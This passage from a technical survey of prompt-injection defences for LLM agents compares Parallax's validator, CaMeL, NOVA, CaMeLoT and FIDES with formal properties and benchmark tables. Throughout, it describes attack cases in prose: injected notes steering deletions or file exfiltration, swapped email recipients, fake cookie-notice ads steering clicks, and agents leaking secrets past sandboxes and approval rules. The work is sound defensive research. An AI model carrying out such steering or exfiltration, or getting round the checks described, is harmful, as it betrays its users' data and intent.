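4. Shield evaluates the call. Suppose that no Tier 0 rule covers the path and that the pattern rules find nothing. The default settings skip the classifier for deletions and send them to Tier 2, where the evaluator receives a request to delete one text file and may well allow it.
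5. The engine recomputes the hash to confirm that nobody has altered the request since the check.
6. Chronicle saves a copy of the file.
7. The flow check finds public data and a change inside the workspace, and allows it.
8. The engine deletes the file, logs the action and returns the result to the agent.

If Ana had asked for `plan-b.md` to be deleted, every step would have received the same input. This is deliberate. Fokou writes of instructions hidden in documents that "the origin of the instruction is irrelevant", because Shield judges only the action. Ignoring the origin makes sense for an action nobody should take, such as sending out the user's passwords, but an ordinary deletion could be either an attack or the user's task, and only the origin of the instruction distinguishes them.

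### The OpenSSH precedent

Fokou models the two processes on OpenSSH, a widely used program for logging in to remote computers. In *Preventing Privilege Escalation*, Provos, Friedl and Honeyman (2003) split its server into an unprivileged child process that handles network traffic and a privileged monitor that performs the few operations requiring superuser rights. The child can request a digital signature, for example, but never receives the private key used to sign.

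The monitor accepts requests from a short table, and the valid entries change as the login proceeds. At first the child may request only encryption parameters and a signature, once each. It may then only ask the monitor to check a user name, after which it may submit a password or other proof of identity. The monitor shuts down if a request is invalid. Provos and colleagues showed that this design would have limited the damage from several serious bugs in earlier versions. The design also left only about a third of the code, including libraries, running with special privileges.

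Parallax copies OpenSSH's two processes faithfully, but the analogy is weaker for the requests that pass between them. OpenSSH's monitor can check a password against its own records, whatever the child process sends, but Parallax's engine has no record of which files Ana wants to keep. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* attributes this difficulty to agent work being open-ended. Agents combine tools as they go and visit arbitrary addresses, the task may change during the conversation, and a policy such as "do not share sensitive data" depends on context that formal rules cannot easily express. OpenSSH's designers could write their table in advance because every login follows the same few steps.

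The two designs also guard against different harms. Privilege separation in OpenSSH stops an attacker from becoming the superuser. Once a user has logged in, though, the child process runs with all of that user's privileges, so an attacker who controls it can run commands as the user. A personal agent has its user's authority from the start, and that authority is enough to delete Ana's file.

### The evaluation

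Fokou first ran the attacks with real models in place. Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Llama 3.1 8B refused every harmful request whether or not Shield was on, so these runs couldn't show whether the validator helped. Fokou then took the model out and sent harmful tool calls directly to Shield, as if an attacker had complete control of the agent. There were 280 calls in nine categories:

| Category | Cases | Missed, default setting | Missed, strictest setting |
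|---|---|---|---|
| Direct instructions | 25 | 1 | 0 |
| Instructions hidden in data | 40 | 0 | 0 |
| Gradual steering over several steps | 30 | 0 | 0 |
| Harmful chains of tool calls | 37 | 1 | 0 |
| Disguised commands | 32 | 0 | 0 |
| Attacks through other agents | 25 | 0 | 0 |
| Attacks on the validator | 26 | 0 | 0 |
| Exploiting the agent's helpfulness | 60 | 1 | 0 |
| Cases meant for human approval | 5 | 0 | 0 |
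| Total | 280 | 3 | 0 |

The default setting blocked 98.9% of the attacks, and the strictest setting blocked 100%. Fokou also submitted 50 legitimate actions, such as installing a package or sending an email. The default setting blocked none of them, and the strictest blocked 18, or 36%. If the strictest setting blocked each legitimate action independently at that rate, it would allow all the actions in a five-action task about 11% of the time.

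The strictest setting applies the classifier to every action, while the default skips it for seven types of action, including writing files, deleting them and sending email, and passes those to the Tier 2 model. The classifier was trained on examples of injected text rather than tool calls, a limit that Fokou acknowledges, and it caused 14 of the 18 false alarms by mistaking ordinary contents for attacks. The Tier 2 model caused the other four by blocking legitimate commands. Commands follow the same route under both settings, so another run of the default might have blocked some of those four too. Fifty actions is also a small sample. A validator that wrongly blocked one legitimate action in 20 would pass all 50 about 8% of the time.

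The 98.9% is probably optimistic for new attacks. Early tests exposed gaps in the rules, and Fokou closed them with new denials and 17 more patterns before reporting results on the refined policy. Fokou fairly describes this as a normal part of maintaining a security policy, but it leaves no unseen attacks to test on. Jing evaluated a similar gate between an agent and the operating system on 313 cases chosen in advance. The full system cut attack success from 98.3% to 7.7% and denied 11.1% of benign tasks. Much of that protection came from an operating-system sandbox, without which 30.8% of attacks succeeded. Jing also repaired defects that the benchmark had exposed, so this wasn't a clean test on unseen attacks either. The two sets of cases are too different to rank the systems.

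Parallax also slows the agent down. Tier 0 takes less than a millisecond, but the classifier and the Tier 2 model each typically take about two seconds per action. Fokou expects to make the classifier much faster.

These tests did not use the agent's own model. The 40 cases of instructions hidden in data contain only the calls that such instructions might produce, not the data or the user's task. The results support the claim that Shield blocks most of the harmful calls in the tests, but they can't show whether a stranger's text influences the calls that Shield permits.

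### Restricting actions and isolating influence

Restricting an agent's actions and isolating it from untrusted text are separate properties. In the earlier notation, where *M* is the model and *H* is the harness, now including its validator:

```
restriction:  for every input x,
              H(M(x)) is a permitted action

isolation:    for every x and x′ that differ only in untrusted text,
              H(M(x)) = H(M(x′))
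```

Restriction can be tested one call at a time, as Fokou did. Isolation is a form of noninterference, so testing it requires a pair of runs and a model that reads the text in question. Neither property implies the other. A mail sorter that can only move messages between folders is tightly restricted, but a stranger may still choose the folder every time. An agent that publishes its user's diary every night, whatever it reads, is perfectly isolated from strangers but not restricted from disclosing private data.

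Parallax provides restriction, which is useful in its own right because a rule against a harmful call applies whether the cause was an attacker, a mistake or a badly chosen goal. But OpenParallax's *Threat Model* goes further, claiming that "the agent cannot cause harm because it cannot act". This argument from missing privileges fails once the harness acts on the model's replies. The document's list of remaining gaps includes persuading the human approver and inferring information from response times, but not steering permitted calls. The paper comes closer to acknowledging this problem. All three attacks that the default setting missed were ambiguous actions, such as deleting a temporary file, and Fokou explains that the evaluator cannot judge these without context that it is deliberately denied.

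Permitted actions can do serious damage. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes two cases. In one, the coding agent Claude Code required approval for many network commands but mistakenly exempted one that tests connections, and instructions hidden in a code file led the agent to send secrets out in the addresses it looked up. In the other, OpenAI's sandboxed agents were allowed to reach a package service and used it to make requests to the wider internet. Fokou reports a related weakness in Parallax. Shield checks the command that runs a script but not what the script does, so a misled agent could write harmful code in one acceptable step and run it in another.

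In their July 2026 survey, *Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety*, Jing, Hu and colleagues divide an agent system at five boundaries and count Parallax among the designs that "decouple the brain from the hands". Their agent-execution boundary is the point where decisions become real actions, and it fails when the system runs a model's output without enough checking. They find research on such checks less systematic than research on attacks through user input or outside content.

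The survey classifies each attack by the first boundary it violates. A poisoned web page counts as a failure at the point where outside content enters the system, even if the harm appears only at execution. Ana's notes file would belong there too, because the stranger's line had determined which file to delete before Shield received the call. For Jing and colleagues, isolation covers what a component can do, how far the system should trust a piece of data, and what authority that data carries. Shield can check whether the agent may delete a file in Ana's project, but it has no record of whose instruction the deletion follows.

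## CaMeL and its successors: fixing the plan before untrusted data is read

A harness doesn't need to trace a deletion back to an instruction if only the user's instructions can put a deletion in the plan. A designer can arrange this by having one model choose every step before any model reads what a stranger wrote. Then a stranger who edits Ana's notes file can't turn a request for a summary into a deletion. Ana's request is harder because she asked for deletions and the file names come from the notes.

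### Two models and a controller

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed dividing the work between two language models. The planner model, which Willison calls privileged, takes the user's request and can issue tool calls. The quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted text, and has no tools. The harness, which Willison calls the controller, runs the tools, stores the results and passes messages between the models.

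The planner never sees the stored text. It works with the names of variables instead. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the exchange goes like this:

1. The planner asks for the latest email. The controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`.
2. The planner asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller puts the email's text into a prompt for the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
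3. The planner asks the controller to display `$VAR2`, and the controller shows the summary to the user.

An instruction hidden in the email may spoil the summary, but it never reaches the model that can call tools.

Willison allows one exception. If the quarantined model's task is to sort text into a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the answer is one of them and then pass it to the planner. An attacker can't fit a new instruction into a label like "urgent" or "not urgent", but may still be able to influence which label the model picks, and the planner may act on it.

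Willison called his own proposal "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and worse to use, and one programming mistake that lets untrusted text reach the planner undoes the protection. It also assumes that everything the user enters is safe, which is false if someone tricks the user into pasting an attacker's text.

A further flaw came to light two years later. In an example from *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025), a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and the meeting notes contain both Bob's address and the document's name. The planner correctly sets out the steps: find the address, fetch the document and send the email. But when the quarantined model reads the notes to find the address, an instruction hidden there can make it return the attacker's address instead. The agent then takes the steps the user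 wanted but sends the document to the attacker.

### CaMeL's program and its labels

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, addresses this flaw by tracking where each value came from. The planner writes the whole plan at the start, as a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the program, calling the tools and the quarantined model. Each value carries labels, called capabilities, that record its sources and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the arguments' labels against a policy for that tool.

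Suppose Ana now asks, "If the notes say the review is over, delete the drafts they list as out of date. Otherwise, ask Bob when it will end." The planner sees only this request and the descriptions of the tools. It might write:

```
notes = read_file("notes.txt")
over  = ask_quarantined("Does this say the review is over?", notes)
if over:
    drafts = ask_quarantined("Which drafts are out of date?", notes)
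    for name in drafts:
        delete_file(name)
else:
    send_email(to=find_contact("Bob"),
               body="When will the review end?")
```

The label on `notes` lists everyone who can edit the file as sources and everyone with shared access to it as permitted readers. Both `over` and `drafts` inherit that label because the quarantined model computed them from the notes. A cautious policy for `delete_file` would require file names to come from a trusted source. These names don't, so the interpreter would stop and prompt Ana. The email would pass, since Bob's address comes from Ana's contacts and the wording comes from the planner. If the email quoted the notes, the interpreter could also check whether Bob was permitted to read them.

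Now suppose a stranger adds `plan-b.md` to the list of old drafts, along with a hidden instruction to send the project's files to an outside address. The files aren't sent, because the program has no line that sends them and the notes can't add one. But `plan-b.md` can still end up in `drafts`. Whether the harness deletes it depends on the policy and, if the policy requires Ana's approval, on whether she notices the name. The stranger can also write that the review is over when it isn't, which makes the program run the deletion branch too early. Because the program deletes files in a loop, the notes also determine how many it deletes.

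### Plan, branches and values

These effects correspond to different guarantees. Take two versions of the notes, *d* and *d′*, that differ only in what strangers wrote:

```
plan integrity:      program(d)   = program(d′)
branch integrity:    path(d)      = path(d′)
value integrity:     arguments(d) = arguments(d′)
```

The path is the sequence of lines the interpreter runs, and the arguments are the values it passes to tools. An agent with all three guarantees would make the same tool calls for both versions, which is the isolation Parallax does not provide.

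CaMeL guarantees plan integrity, because the planner finishes the program before any model reads the notes. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, use the established name control-flow integrity for this property. By their definition, an agent's execution must stay within a plan that the user's instruction and other trusted information determine. Untrusted data may select among the branches of that plan but may not add any. (The guarantee does not automatically carry over to a group of agents, because one agent may write another's instructions.)

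Values get weaker protection than the plan. The labels only let the interpreter refuse to use a doubtful value at a sink, and they can't make `drafts` correct. Without a policy for `delete_file`, the interpreter passes it the false name. A strict policy blocks the false name but also blocks the true ones, because it treats every name from the notes alike.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) demonstrates the same trade-off with computer-checked proofs about small model agents. In one, the program reads a user's private notes and an attacker's email, asks the quarantined model for a reply based on both, and sends the reply to the attacker. Without labels, an injected instruction can make the quarantined model copy the notes into the reply. With labels, the reply counts as private because one of its inputs was private, so the agent never sends it. This holds however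 the quarantined model behaves, but it also means the agent can't send an honest reply.

Branches can bypass the labels through implicit flows, which taint tracking usually misses. Dongol changes the program so that it sends the attacker a 1 or a 0, depending on the quarantined model's answer. Both numbers are constants that the planner wrote, so they are public and pass the check. An injected instruction can make the answer depend on the private notes, and the attacker then learns something about the notes from which number arrives.

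CaMeL's strict mode, which Dongol doesn't model, also labels what happens inside a branch according to the data that selected the branch. In Ana's program, the message to Bob would then carry the notes' label even though it quotes nothing from them. A policy that allowed the message because the planner wrote its text might now block it, so closing this gap brings back label creep.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) makes a slightly different distinction, between control-flow integrity and data-flow security, where the latter covers both the arguments and the values that decide conditions. It helps to distinguish arguments from condition values, because a check at the tool call examines the arguments but may have no record of why the program reached that call.

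### What the fixed plan costs

A planner that can't see tool results has to write the code that handles them in advance. To extract an email's sender, for example, it must know the name of the sender field without seeing the email. Peters-Gill and colleagues therefore had to add a full description of each tool's output to their benchmarks. An ordinary agent doesn't need these descriptions because it reads the output and adapts.

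Narisetty and colleagues report that in CaMeL's original evaluation, the same model completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks with CaMeL and 84% without it, and that CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens. In more recent tests by Peters-Gill and colleagues on industrial tasks, where several agents share the work, CaMeL lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models. For the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the loss was smaller but still averaged 13.4 points. Better planners seem to write better programs in advance.

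### When the data contains the steps

For some requests, the necessary steps depend on the data. If a user says "Do what Julia's email asks", the planner can't choose the steps without reading the email, and reading it would end the isolation. The problem also arises in tasks that look fully specified. For example, a user asks an agent to buy a pair of shoes, and at checkout the shop requires a login code that it has just sent by email. The agent then has to read the inbox, which the user didn't mention in the request.

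*AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) is a benchmark built from such cases. Its 60 tasks cover shopping, software projects and daily life, and average about seven steps each. In every task, the agent has to revise its plan along the way and follow at least one helpful instruction from a third party. By the paper's count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks need this kind of replanning, so a defence can score well on AgentDojo by sticking to its initial plan.

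CaMeL completed none of the 60 tasks with any of the four main models:

| Model | Undefended | CaMeL | DRIFT |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 53.3% | 0.0% | 30.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 51.7% | 0.0% | 36.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 3.5 | 60.0% | 0.0% | 33.3% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10.0% | 0.0% | 11.7% |

These are completion rates without an attack. CaMeL's attack success rate was also zero, but an agent that can't finish its own tasks gives an attacker few opportunities. DRIFT, which starts from a plan and uses a separate validator to approve departures from it, retained some of the utility that CaMeL lost. Attacks on it succeeded between 0.8% and 5.9% of the time.

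The zeros don't show how often real work needs replanning, since Li and colleagues wrote every task to require it. They also used older models because newer ones have probably trained on the standard attack. A better planner could anticipate some of these steps. For example, login codes are common enough that a program for buying shoes could include a branch that checks the inbox for one.

But plan integrity is only as useful as the plan is specific. A program could read a to-do list from an email, ask the quarantined model which tool each item needs, and have a branch for every tool the agent has. The planner could write this program before reading the email, so it would have full plan integrity, but it would also let whoever wrote the email call any tool. When a request leaves every step to the data, the plan can satisfy the definition while giving the user no protection.

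### Planning for a screen the planner cannot see

Fixing the plan in advance is harder for computer-use agents, which take screenshots as input and return clicks and keystrokes. The model usually gets a new screenshot after every action, because a page may load slowly, show a pop-up or move a button. In a CaMeL-style agent, the planner is not allowed to see any screenshots.

In January 2026, Foerster and colleagues showed that such an agent can still do some useful work. Their planner writes the complete program first, including branches for the situations it expects. A vision model then takes the quarantined role and answers the program's questions about the screen. They call the planning method NOVA, and it has the program repeat a cycle:

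1. Observe: the vision model describes the current screen.
2. Verify: a quarantined model compares that description with a condition the planner wrote in advance, such as "the browser shows the login page", and the interpreter picks a branch from the result.
3. Act: the program clicks or types, often at coordinates that the vision model has supplied.

The programs are long because they have to cover many situations. CaMeL's AgentDojo plans averaged 4.9 tool calls and 3.7 branches, whereas NOVA plans averaged 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches. About half of a plan consists of fallbacks that don't run on a given attempt. Without NOVA's guidance, plans averaged 11.3 branches and solved 11 of 60 tasks in three attempts, compared with 35 when the same vision model had the guidance.

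### How much performance remains

Foerster and colleagues used OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in real desktop applications. They took the tasks that each undefended agent had solved, leaving out 30 that OSWorld can't check automatically, and counted how many the isolated version could still solve:

| Agent's original model | Solved undefended | Still solved, one attempt | Three attempts | Five attempts |
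|---|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | 60 | 25 (42%) | 35 (58%) | 39 (65%) |
| OpenCUA-32B | 76 | 22 (29%) | 37 (49%) | 48 (63%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 (28%) | 57 (52%) | 62 (57%) |

The paper's headline figure is that the design retains up to 57% of a frontier model's performance. This is the last entry for Claude, and it counts a task as solved if any of five separately written plans succeeds. Foerster and colleagues say it is an upper bound because it assumes something can pick out the successful plan. Running several plans on a real computer is also a problem because the failed attempts click on things too. The 28% from a single attempt is closer to what a user would experience.

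They also report that the design improved a small open model by up to 19%. That is a relative gain, from 24.4% to 29.0% on the whole benchmark, and it too relies on repeated attempts, here three. With one attempt, the score by the same count would be about 22%, slightly below the undefended model. The isolated version also uses a separate planner, which accounts for much of its ability. Three vision models tested on the same 60 tasks all scored between 65% and 68% with five attempts. The choice of planner mattered much more. On a set of 17 tasks, GPT-5 solved 12 and the next best of nine planners solved 10.

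Fixed plans work better on changing screens than one might expect, but the loss in performance is still large. Better planners should reduce it, and retrying may help where a failed attempt does no damage.

### Branch steering

A web page can't add steps to a NOVA plan, but it can affect the vision model's output, which the program uses to choose branches and decide where to click. Foerster and colleagues call this kind of attack branch steering. In their main example, an advertisement imitates a cookie notice. The plan already contains a routine for dismissing such notices, so the agent clicks the advertisement and opens the attacker's site.

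Their term covers wrong values as well as wrong branches, and the two are hard to separate for a computer-use agent. A call to `send_email` always sends an email, whatever its arguments, but a call to `click(x, y)` might close a window, delete a file or place an order, depending on what is at that point on the screen. An attacker who can influence where an existing click lands doesn't need to add one. Plan integrity still holds formally, since the agent makes only the calls that the planner wrote, but it rules out far less when those calls have no fixed effect.

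For the same reason, CaMeL's policies are hard to apply here. A policy can forbid sending a private file to an outsider, but there is no obvious rule for which coordinates are safe. Foerster and colleagues therefore ran the agent without policies and added redundant checks. One compared the vision model's answer with the DOM, the browser's structured description of the page. Another used a second model to judge whether the answer fitted the screenshot and the instruction.

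Neither the DOM check nor the second model was enough. The DOM check caught the false cookie notice in one type of advertisement but missed it in another. The second model could not reliably tell false notices from real ones without raising many false alarms. A different attack, which made small changes to an advertisement's pixels, got past the second model even on a setting that heavily favoured security over usefulness. These attacks assumed a strong attacker who knew the task and could roughly predict the plan. That assumption is plausible because NOVA's plans share routines for common events such as cookie notices, which improves the agent's performance but also makes its behaviour easier to predict.

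Long plans also give an attacker more routes to choose from. A program with 40 yes-or-no branches in sequence has 2^40 routes through it, or about a trillion, but only 41 if one side of each branch ends the program. Real plans fall somewhere in between, and an attacker can't control every branch. But the fallbacks that help a plan cope with an unfamiliar screen also add routes that an attacker can select by changing what the screen shows.

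The redundancy also increased token use. Foerster and colleagues reported that the isolated agent's token overhead was 1.88 times the undefended agent's usage, and 6.57 times with the second model's checks. When they applied NOVA to FIDES, which calls its planner again at every step, the overhead was 29.6 times.

### Checking the program before it runs

Because CaMeL's plan is a complete program, other software can examine it before any tool runs. CaMeL itself checks one call at a time during execution, so if the tenth step breaks a policy, the agent may already have carried out the first nine.

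*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, September 2026) adds a check at the planning stage. It converts the program into a finite-state machine, a map of the points the program can reach and the moves between them. It labels each point with the tool being called and whether the arguments come from untrusted sources. A standard program called a model checker then tests the map against rules in temporal logic, a notation for stating what happens always, eventually or before something else.

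Three of their rules, lightly simplified, show the range:

```
always:  if the agent sends a direct message, the recipient is trusted
until:   no isolating a computer until the agent has confirmed which one
always:  if the agent opens a ticket, it eventually resolves or escalates it
```

CaMeL can enforce the rule about recipients when the call arrives. It has no natural way to express the rule about tickets, because an agent breaks that rule by failing to do something rather than by making any single call.

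In their worked example, a three-step plan reads a channel's messages, has the quarantined model find Bob's address in them, and sends Bob a message. The map has five points, including the start and the end. The address becomes tainted when the quarantined model returns it, and by the third step the recipient is tainted too, which breaks the first rule. The model checker returns the path that led to the violation. CaMeLoT turns this path into a plain-language explanation, which the planner uses to try to repair the program.

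The checker ignores the conditions on branches and assumes that any branch could run. This is crude, but it means that a rule passes only if it holds on every path, including any path an attacker selects through branch steering. If Ana's organisation required a backup before every deletion, CaMeLoT could confirm that the program obeyed the rule on both branches, whatever was in the notes about the review. It couldn't confirm that the deletion branch was the right one to take.

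### What CaMeLoT covers and blocks

Nikolaou and colleagues could express 22 of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies in a form that CaMeLoT can check in advance. The other six depend on facts that only exist at run time, such as who has access to a file, so CaMeL still has to check the calls as they happen.

They then ran both systems on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks, with no attacks and with Claude Haiku 4.5 as the planner:

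| Result | Tasks |
|---|---|
| Both allowed the plan and it worked | 42 |
| Both blocked the plan | 17 |
| Only CaMeLoT's run succeeded | 9 |
| Only CaMeL's run succeeded | 7 |
| Both allowed the plan but it failed | 22 |

Excluding the last row, the systems agreed on 59 of 75 tasks. Both systems also blocked the same 17 harmless tasks. Each system alone completed about half of the 97 tasks. Nikolaou and colleagues intend each plan to pass both checks, which would lower the success rate further unless the planner could repair rejected plans. The experiment mostly ran without repair, so its results probably understate what the full system can do.

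Much of CaMeLoT's overhead arises because it treats a value as tainted whenever it can't tell in advance whether the value will be trustworthy. For instance, a calendar entry's description might come from the user or from a stranger, and the program text doesn't show which. Nikolaou and colleagues argue that a false alarm usually adds one more round of planning, while catching a real violation early avoids every model and tool call that would have preceded it. This seems fair for long tasks when the plan can be repaired, but if the task needs an address from an email, rewriting the plan won't make that address trusted.

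Another experiment tested seven altered versions of a safe plan for a security analyst, each breaking a different rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The rules were chosen to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the result shows the wider range of rules CaMeLoT can enforce and isn't a fair comparison of the two systems. The same setting also exposes a gap in plan integrity itself. When a user asked to skip the approval step because time was short, the planner wrote a plan that skipped it. No untrusted text was involved, and CaMeL allowed the plan.

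CaMeLoT can also derive rules from the user's request. A model proposes requirements from a fixed list of types, and ordinary code turns them into logic. On AgentDojo, the model identified exactly the right state-changing tools for 85 of the 97 tasks. A wrong proposal could block a good plan or let an incomplete one through, so these rules are less dependable than rules written by a person.

### Attacks that respond to the defence

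Almost all of these results come from fixed sets of attacks. Narisetty and colleagues point out in their June 2026 paper that twelve earlier defences that relied on detecting or resisting injections also looked strong on such sets. When researchers designed attacks specifically against those defences, most of them failed over 90% of the time.

Their own experiment tests Progent instead of CaMeL. Fixed code enforces Progent's rules, but a language model writes them and may loosen them after reading tool results. Untrusted text can therefore influence what Progent permits, whereas CaMeL's planner reads no untrusted text.

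They ran the agent on the first eight user tasks in three of AgentDojo's settings, paired with every injected task, and repeated the whole study three times. The averages mentioned earlier conceal large differences between settings:

| Measure | Undefended | Progent, standard attack | Progent, tailored attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attack success, banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Attack success, Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
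| Attack success, workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| User tasks completed, average | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

The workspace row can't show whether Progent works, because the model did not follow the injections there even without a defence. On Slack, the tailored attack did worse than the standard one. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the changes meant to get past Progent also made the attack less persuasive to the agent. If so, the low figure is due as much to the weakness of the attack as to the strength of the defence. The defended agent also completed far fewer tasks and made about 15 times as many model calls per task.

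Narisetty and colleagues leave CaMeL and stronger attacks to future work, particularly attacks that use only actions the agent already has permission to take. Against a fixed plan, such attacks target values and branches, which plan integrity doesn't protect.

They also list problems that would remain even if the checks worked perfectly. Someone has to decide which data to trust, and a wrong label at the start makes every later check wrong. CaMeL's own developers have demonstrated ways to leak information through its interpreter.

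Narisetty and colleagues consider the deepest problem to be ordinary tasks in which untrusted data must lead to an action, such as adding a meeting to the calendar if an email proposes one. Systems such as CaMeL can ask the user to approve the action, but people who see many requests tend to approve them out of habit. Nobody has yet worked out in general which of these tasks an agent can carry out securely.

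## FIDES: labelling everything the model has read

When an email proposes a meeting, the user may want the agent to read it and act on it. CaMeL's planner can handle this only by writing a branch for it in advance. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues at Microsoft published in May 2025, lets the planner choose each step after seeing the result of the previous one, but the harness records how trustworthy and how secret the material the planner has read is, and limits the planner's tool calls accordingly.

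### The labelled loop

FIDES keeps the ordinary agent loop and puts a label on each message. Nobody can say for certain which parts of its context a model used, so the harness assumes that it used all of them. (Some other systems try to estimate which inputs mattered.) Slightly simplified, the loop looks like this:

```
context = developer's instructions + user's request   (trusted, public)

repeat:
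    reply = model(context)
    label(reply) = join of the labels of everything in context
    if reply is an answer: return it to the user
    if the policy forbids this call with these labels: block it
    result = run the tool
    label(result) = join of the labels of the call, its arguments
                    and any stored data the tool read
    context = context + reply + result
```

In the paper's formal version, a forbidden call ends the run. In the experiments, the harness instead reported the violation to the planner, which could then try another approach.

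Anything a tool writes to storage takes on the label of the tool call, so an agent that has read a stranger's message can't remove the message's label by saving the text to a file and reading it back.

A label can apply to a single field of a result. In an email, for example, the sender's address may count as trusted if the mail servers have authenticated it, while the subject and body remain untrusted.

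### Two policies

The policy for consequential actions allows a tool call only if the decision to make the call and all of its arguments are trusted. The confidentiality policy allows data to leave through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is permitted to read the data.

The second policy is useful even when nobody is attacking. In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control: Moving toward secure, autonomous agents*, Alex asks an agent to handle unanswered emails. One is from Priya and previews the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who would like to know the figures but isn't yet allowed to. Once the agent has read both emails, only people who could read both may read its replies:

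```
{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}
```

The harness therefore won't send Marco a reply without asking Alex first. If Priya had copied Marco in, the intersection would be {Alex, Marco} and the harness could send the reply without asking.

An agent with only the confidentiality policy is still open to prompt injection, because untrusted text can determine the action as long as no data goes to someone who shouldn't receive it. An agent with only the policy for consequential actions can still send a secret to an outsider, provided nothing untrusted has influenced the decision. Costa and colleagues assume that the user intended such a disclosure. Enforcing both policies gives the strongest protection but also blocks the most work.

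### Hiding results in variables

With labels alone, an agent that has read one email can do almost nothing consequential afterwards. FIDES reduces this label creep with variables like those in Willison's design, but it uses them selectively. When a tool returns a result, the harness compares each field's label with the context's. If showing the field to the planner would raise the context's label, the harness stores the field in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner sees all other fields directly.

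The planner can still pass a variable to a tool or use the quarantined model to query it. Unlike CaMeL's planner, it can also inspect the variable as a last resort, which puts its contents into the context and raises the context's label for the rest of the run.

A trusted call can have untrusted arguments, because the harness fills in a variable's contents only when it runs the call. Whether that is safe depends on the policy. Costa and colleagues describe a rule for messages that requires a trusted recipient but accepts an untrusted body. The policies they tested on AgentDojo were looser. For tools such as sending money or deleting a file, the harness checked the label of the call but not those of its arguments. It allowed an email if either the call was trusted or the recipients had permission to read the contents.

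Willison's attack on the request to send Bob a document would still work under those rules. In CaMeL's terms, the tested policies protect the plan but not the values in it, so the call to send the email is trusted even if the quarantined model has supplied the attacker's address.

The planner can also learn things about text that is hidden from it. In one of the paper's traces, from a simpler agent that has variables but no quarantined model, the user asks the agent to add Alice to the Slack channel with the fewest messages. The planner can't read the messages or the channels' names, but it can see how many messages each channel returned, and it chooses the empty one. Anyone able to post in that channel could have changed the choice. This is hardly an attack, since the user asked for a result that depends on the messages, but it lets untrusted people influence the planner while the harness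 still treats its context as trusted.

### Three tasks with the same emails

Costa and colleagues use three requests to show what each part of the design adds. Their informal rule for judging the results is that a tool call is safe if the model generated it from trusted inputs.

In the first, the user asks the agent to read the top three emails and send them to someone as a Slack message. An ordinary agent breaks the rule because the emails are in its context when it writes the second call. With variables, the planner never reads them:

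```
read_emails(number=3)
send_message(to=user, message=#read_emails_0)
```

The second request is for a summary of the emails instead. Some model now has to read them, so the planner uses the quarantined one:

```
read_emails(number=3)
query_llm("Summarize ...", input=#read_emails_0)
send_message(to=user, message=#query_llm_0)
```

As in Willison's design, an injection can spoil the summary but can't change the recipient or add a call.

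Both of these tasks are data-independent, meaning that the same sequence of tool calls completes them whatever the data contains. A task is data-dependent if the right sequence depends on the data. The third request is of this type: check the emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, create the calendar event. The planner has to learn something from the emails before it can decide whether to make the last call. It could inspect them, but then its context would be untrusted and the policy would block the event. FIDES instead lets it ask a question with a restricted answer:

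```
read_emails(number=3)
query_llm("Is there a meeting request?", input=#read_emails_0, output=bool)
inspect(#query_llm_0)
query_llm("Extract the event details", input=#read_emails_0, output=event details)
set_event(#query_llm_1)
```

The planner receives only "true" or "false". This still breaks the informal rule, because the answer came from untrusted text. Costa and colleagues propose relaxing the rule for answers this small. The date, time and participants never enter the planner's context, but they are still whatever the email's sender wrote.

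The FIDES paper classifies 77 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks as data-independent, 51 of which need a quarantined model, and the other 20 as data-dependent. Data-dependent tasks are much less common in the workspace setting (two of 40) than in banking (seven of 16) or Slack (nine of 21).

### Limiting an answer by its type

To decide when an answer is small enough, FIDES adds a second lattice, which orders types of data by how much information they can carry:

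```
bool   ⊑   one of {a, b, c}   ⊑   string
1 bit      about 1.6 bits         no fixed bound
```

Each piece of data has both a security label and a type. An answer about a stranger's email might be ((untrusted, public), bool). The harness enforces the type through constrained decoding, which prevents the quarantined model from producing any token that doesn't fit the required format. A policy can then allow a consequential action to use an untrusted yes or no, but not an untrusted string.

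A one-bit answer can still determine whether a $50,000 invoice gets paid, so a policy that accepts such answers has to consider what they determine as well as their length.

The lattice also doesn't record the number of answers. The join of two `bool` types is `bool`, so a context with twenty yes-or-no answers about a stranger's text has the same type as a context with one, even though twenty answers have 2^20, or about a million, possible combinations. A policy meant to limit total influence would need a separate count.

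There is little evidence yet on how well this works in practice. Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of the agent they tested, because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need it. Microsoft's later post still lists it among future directions.

### Explicit secrecy

Costa and colleagues prove that the labelled loop can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. Let *d1* and *d2* be two versions of the data that the agent's tools can reach, which agree on everything public but may differ in their secrets. The notation for this is d1 =L d2. When the agent runs on *d1*, it takes a particular path, and *g* is the function that describes what the steps on that path do to the data. Explicit secrecy requires:

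```
if a run on d1 takes a path with effect g,
then for every d2 with d1 =L d2:    g(d1) =L g(d2)
```

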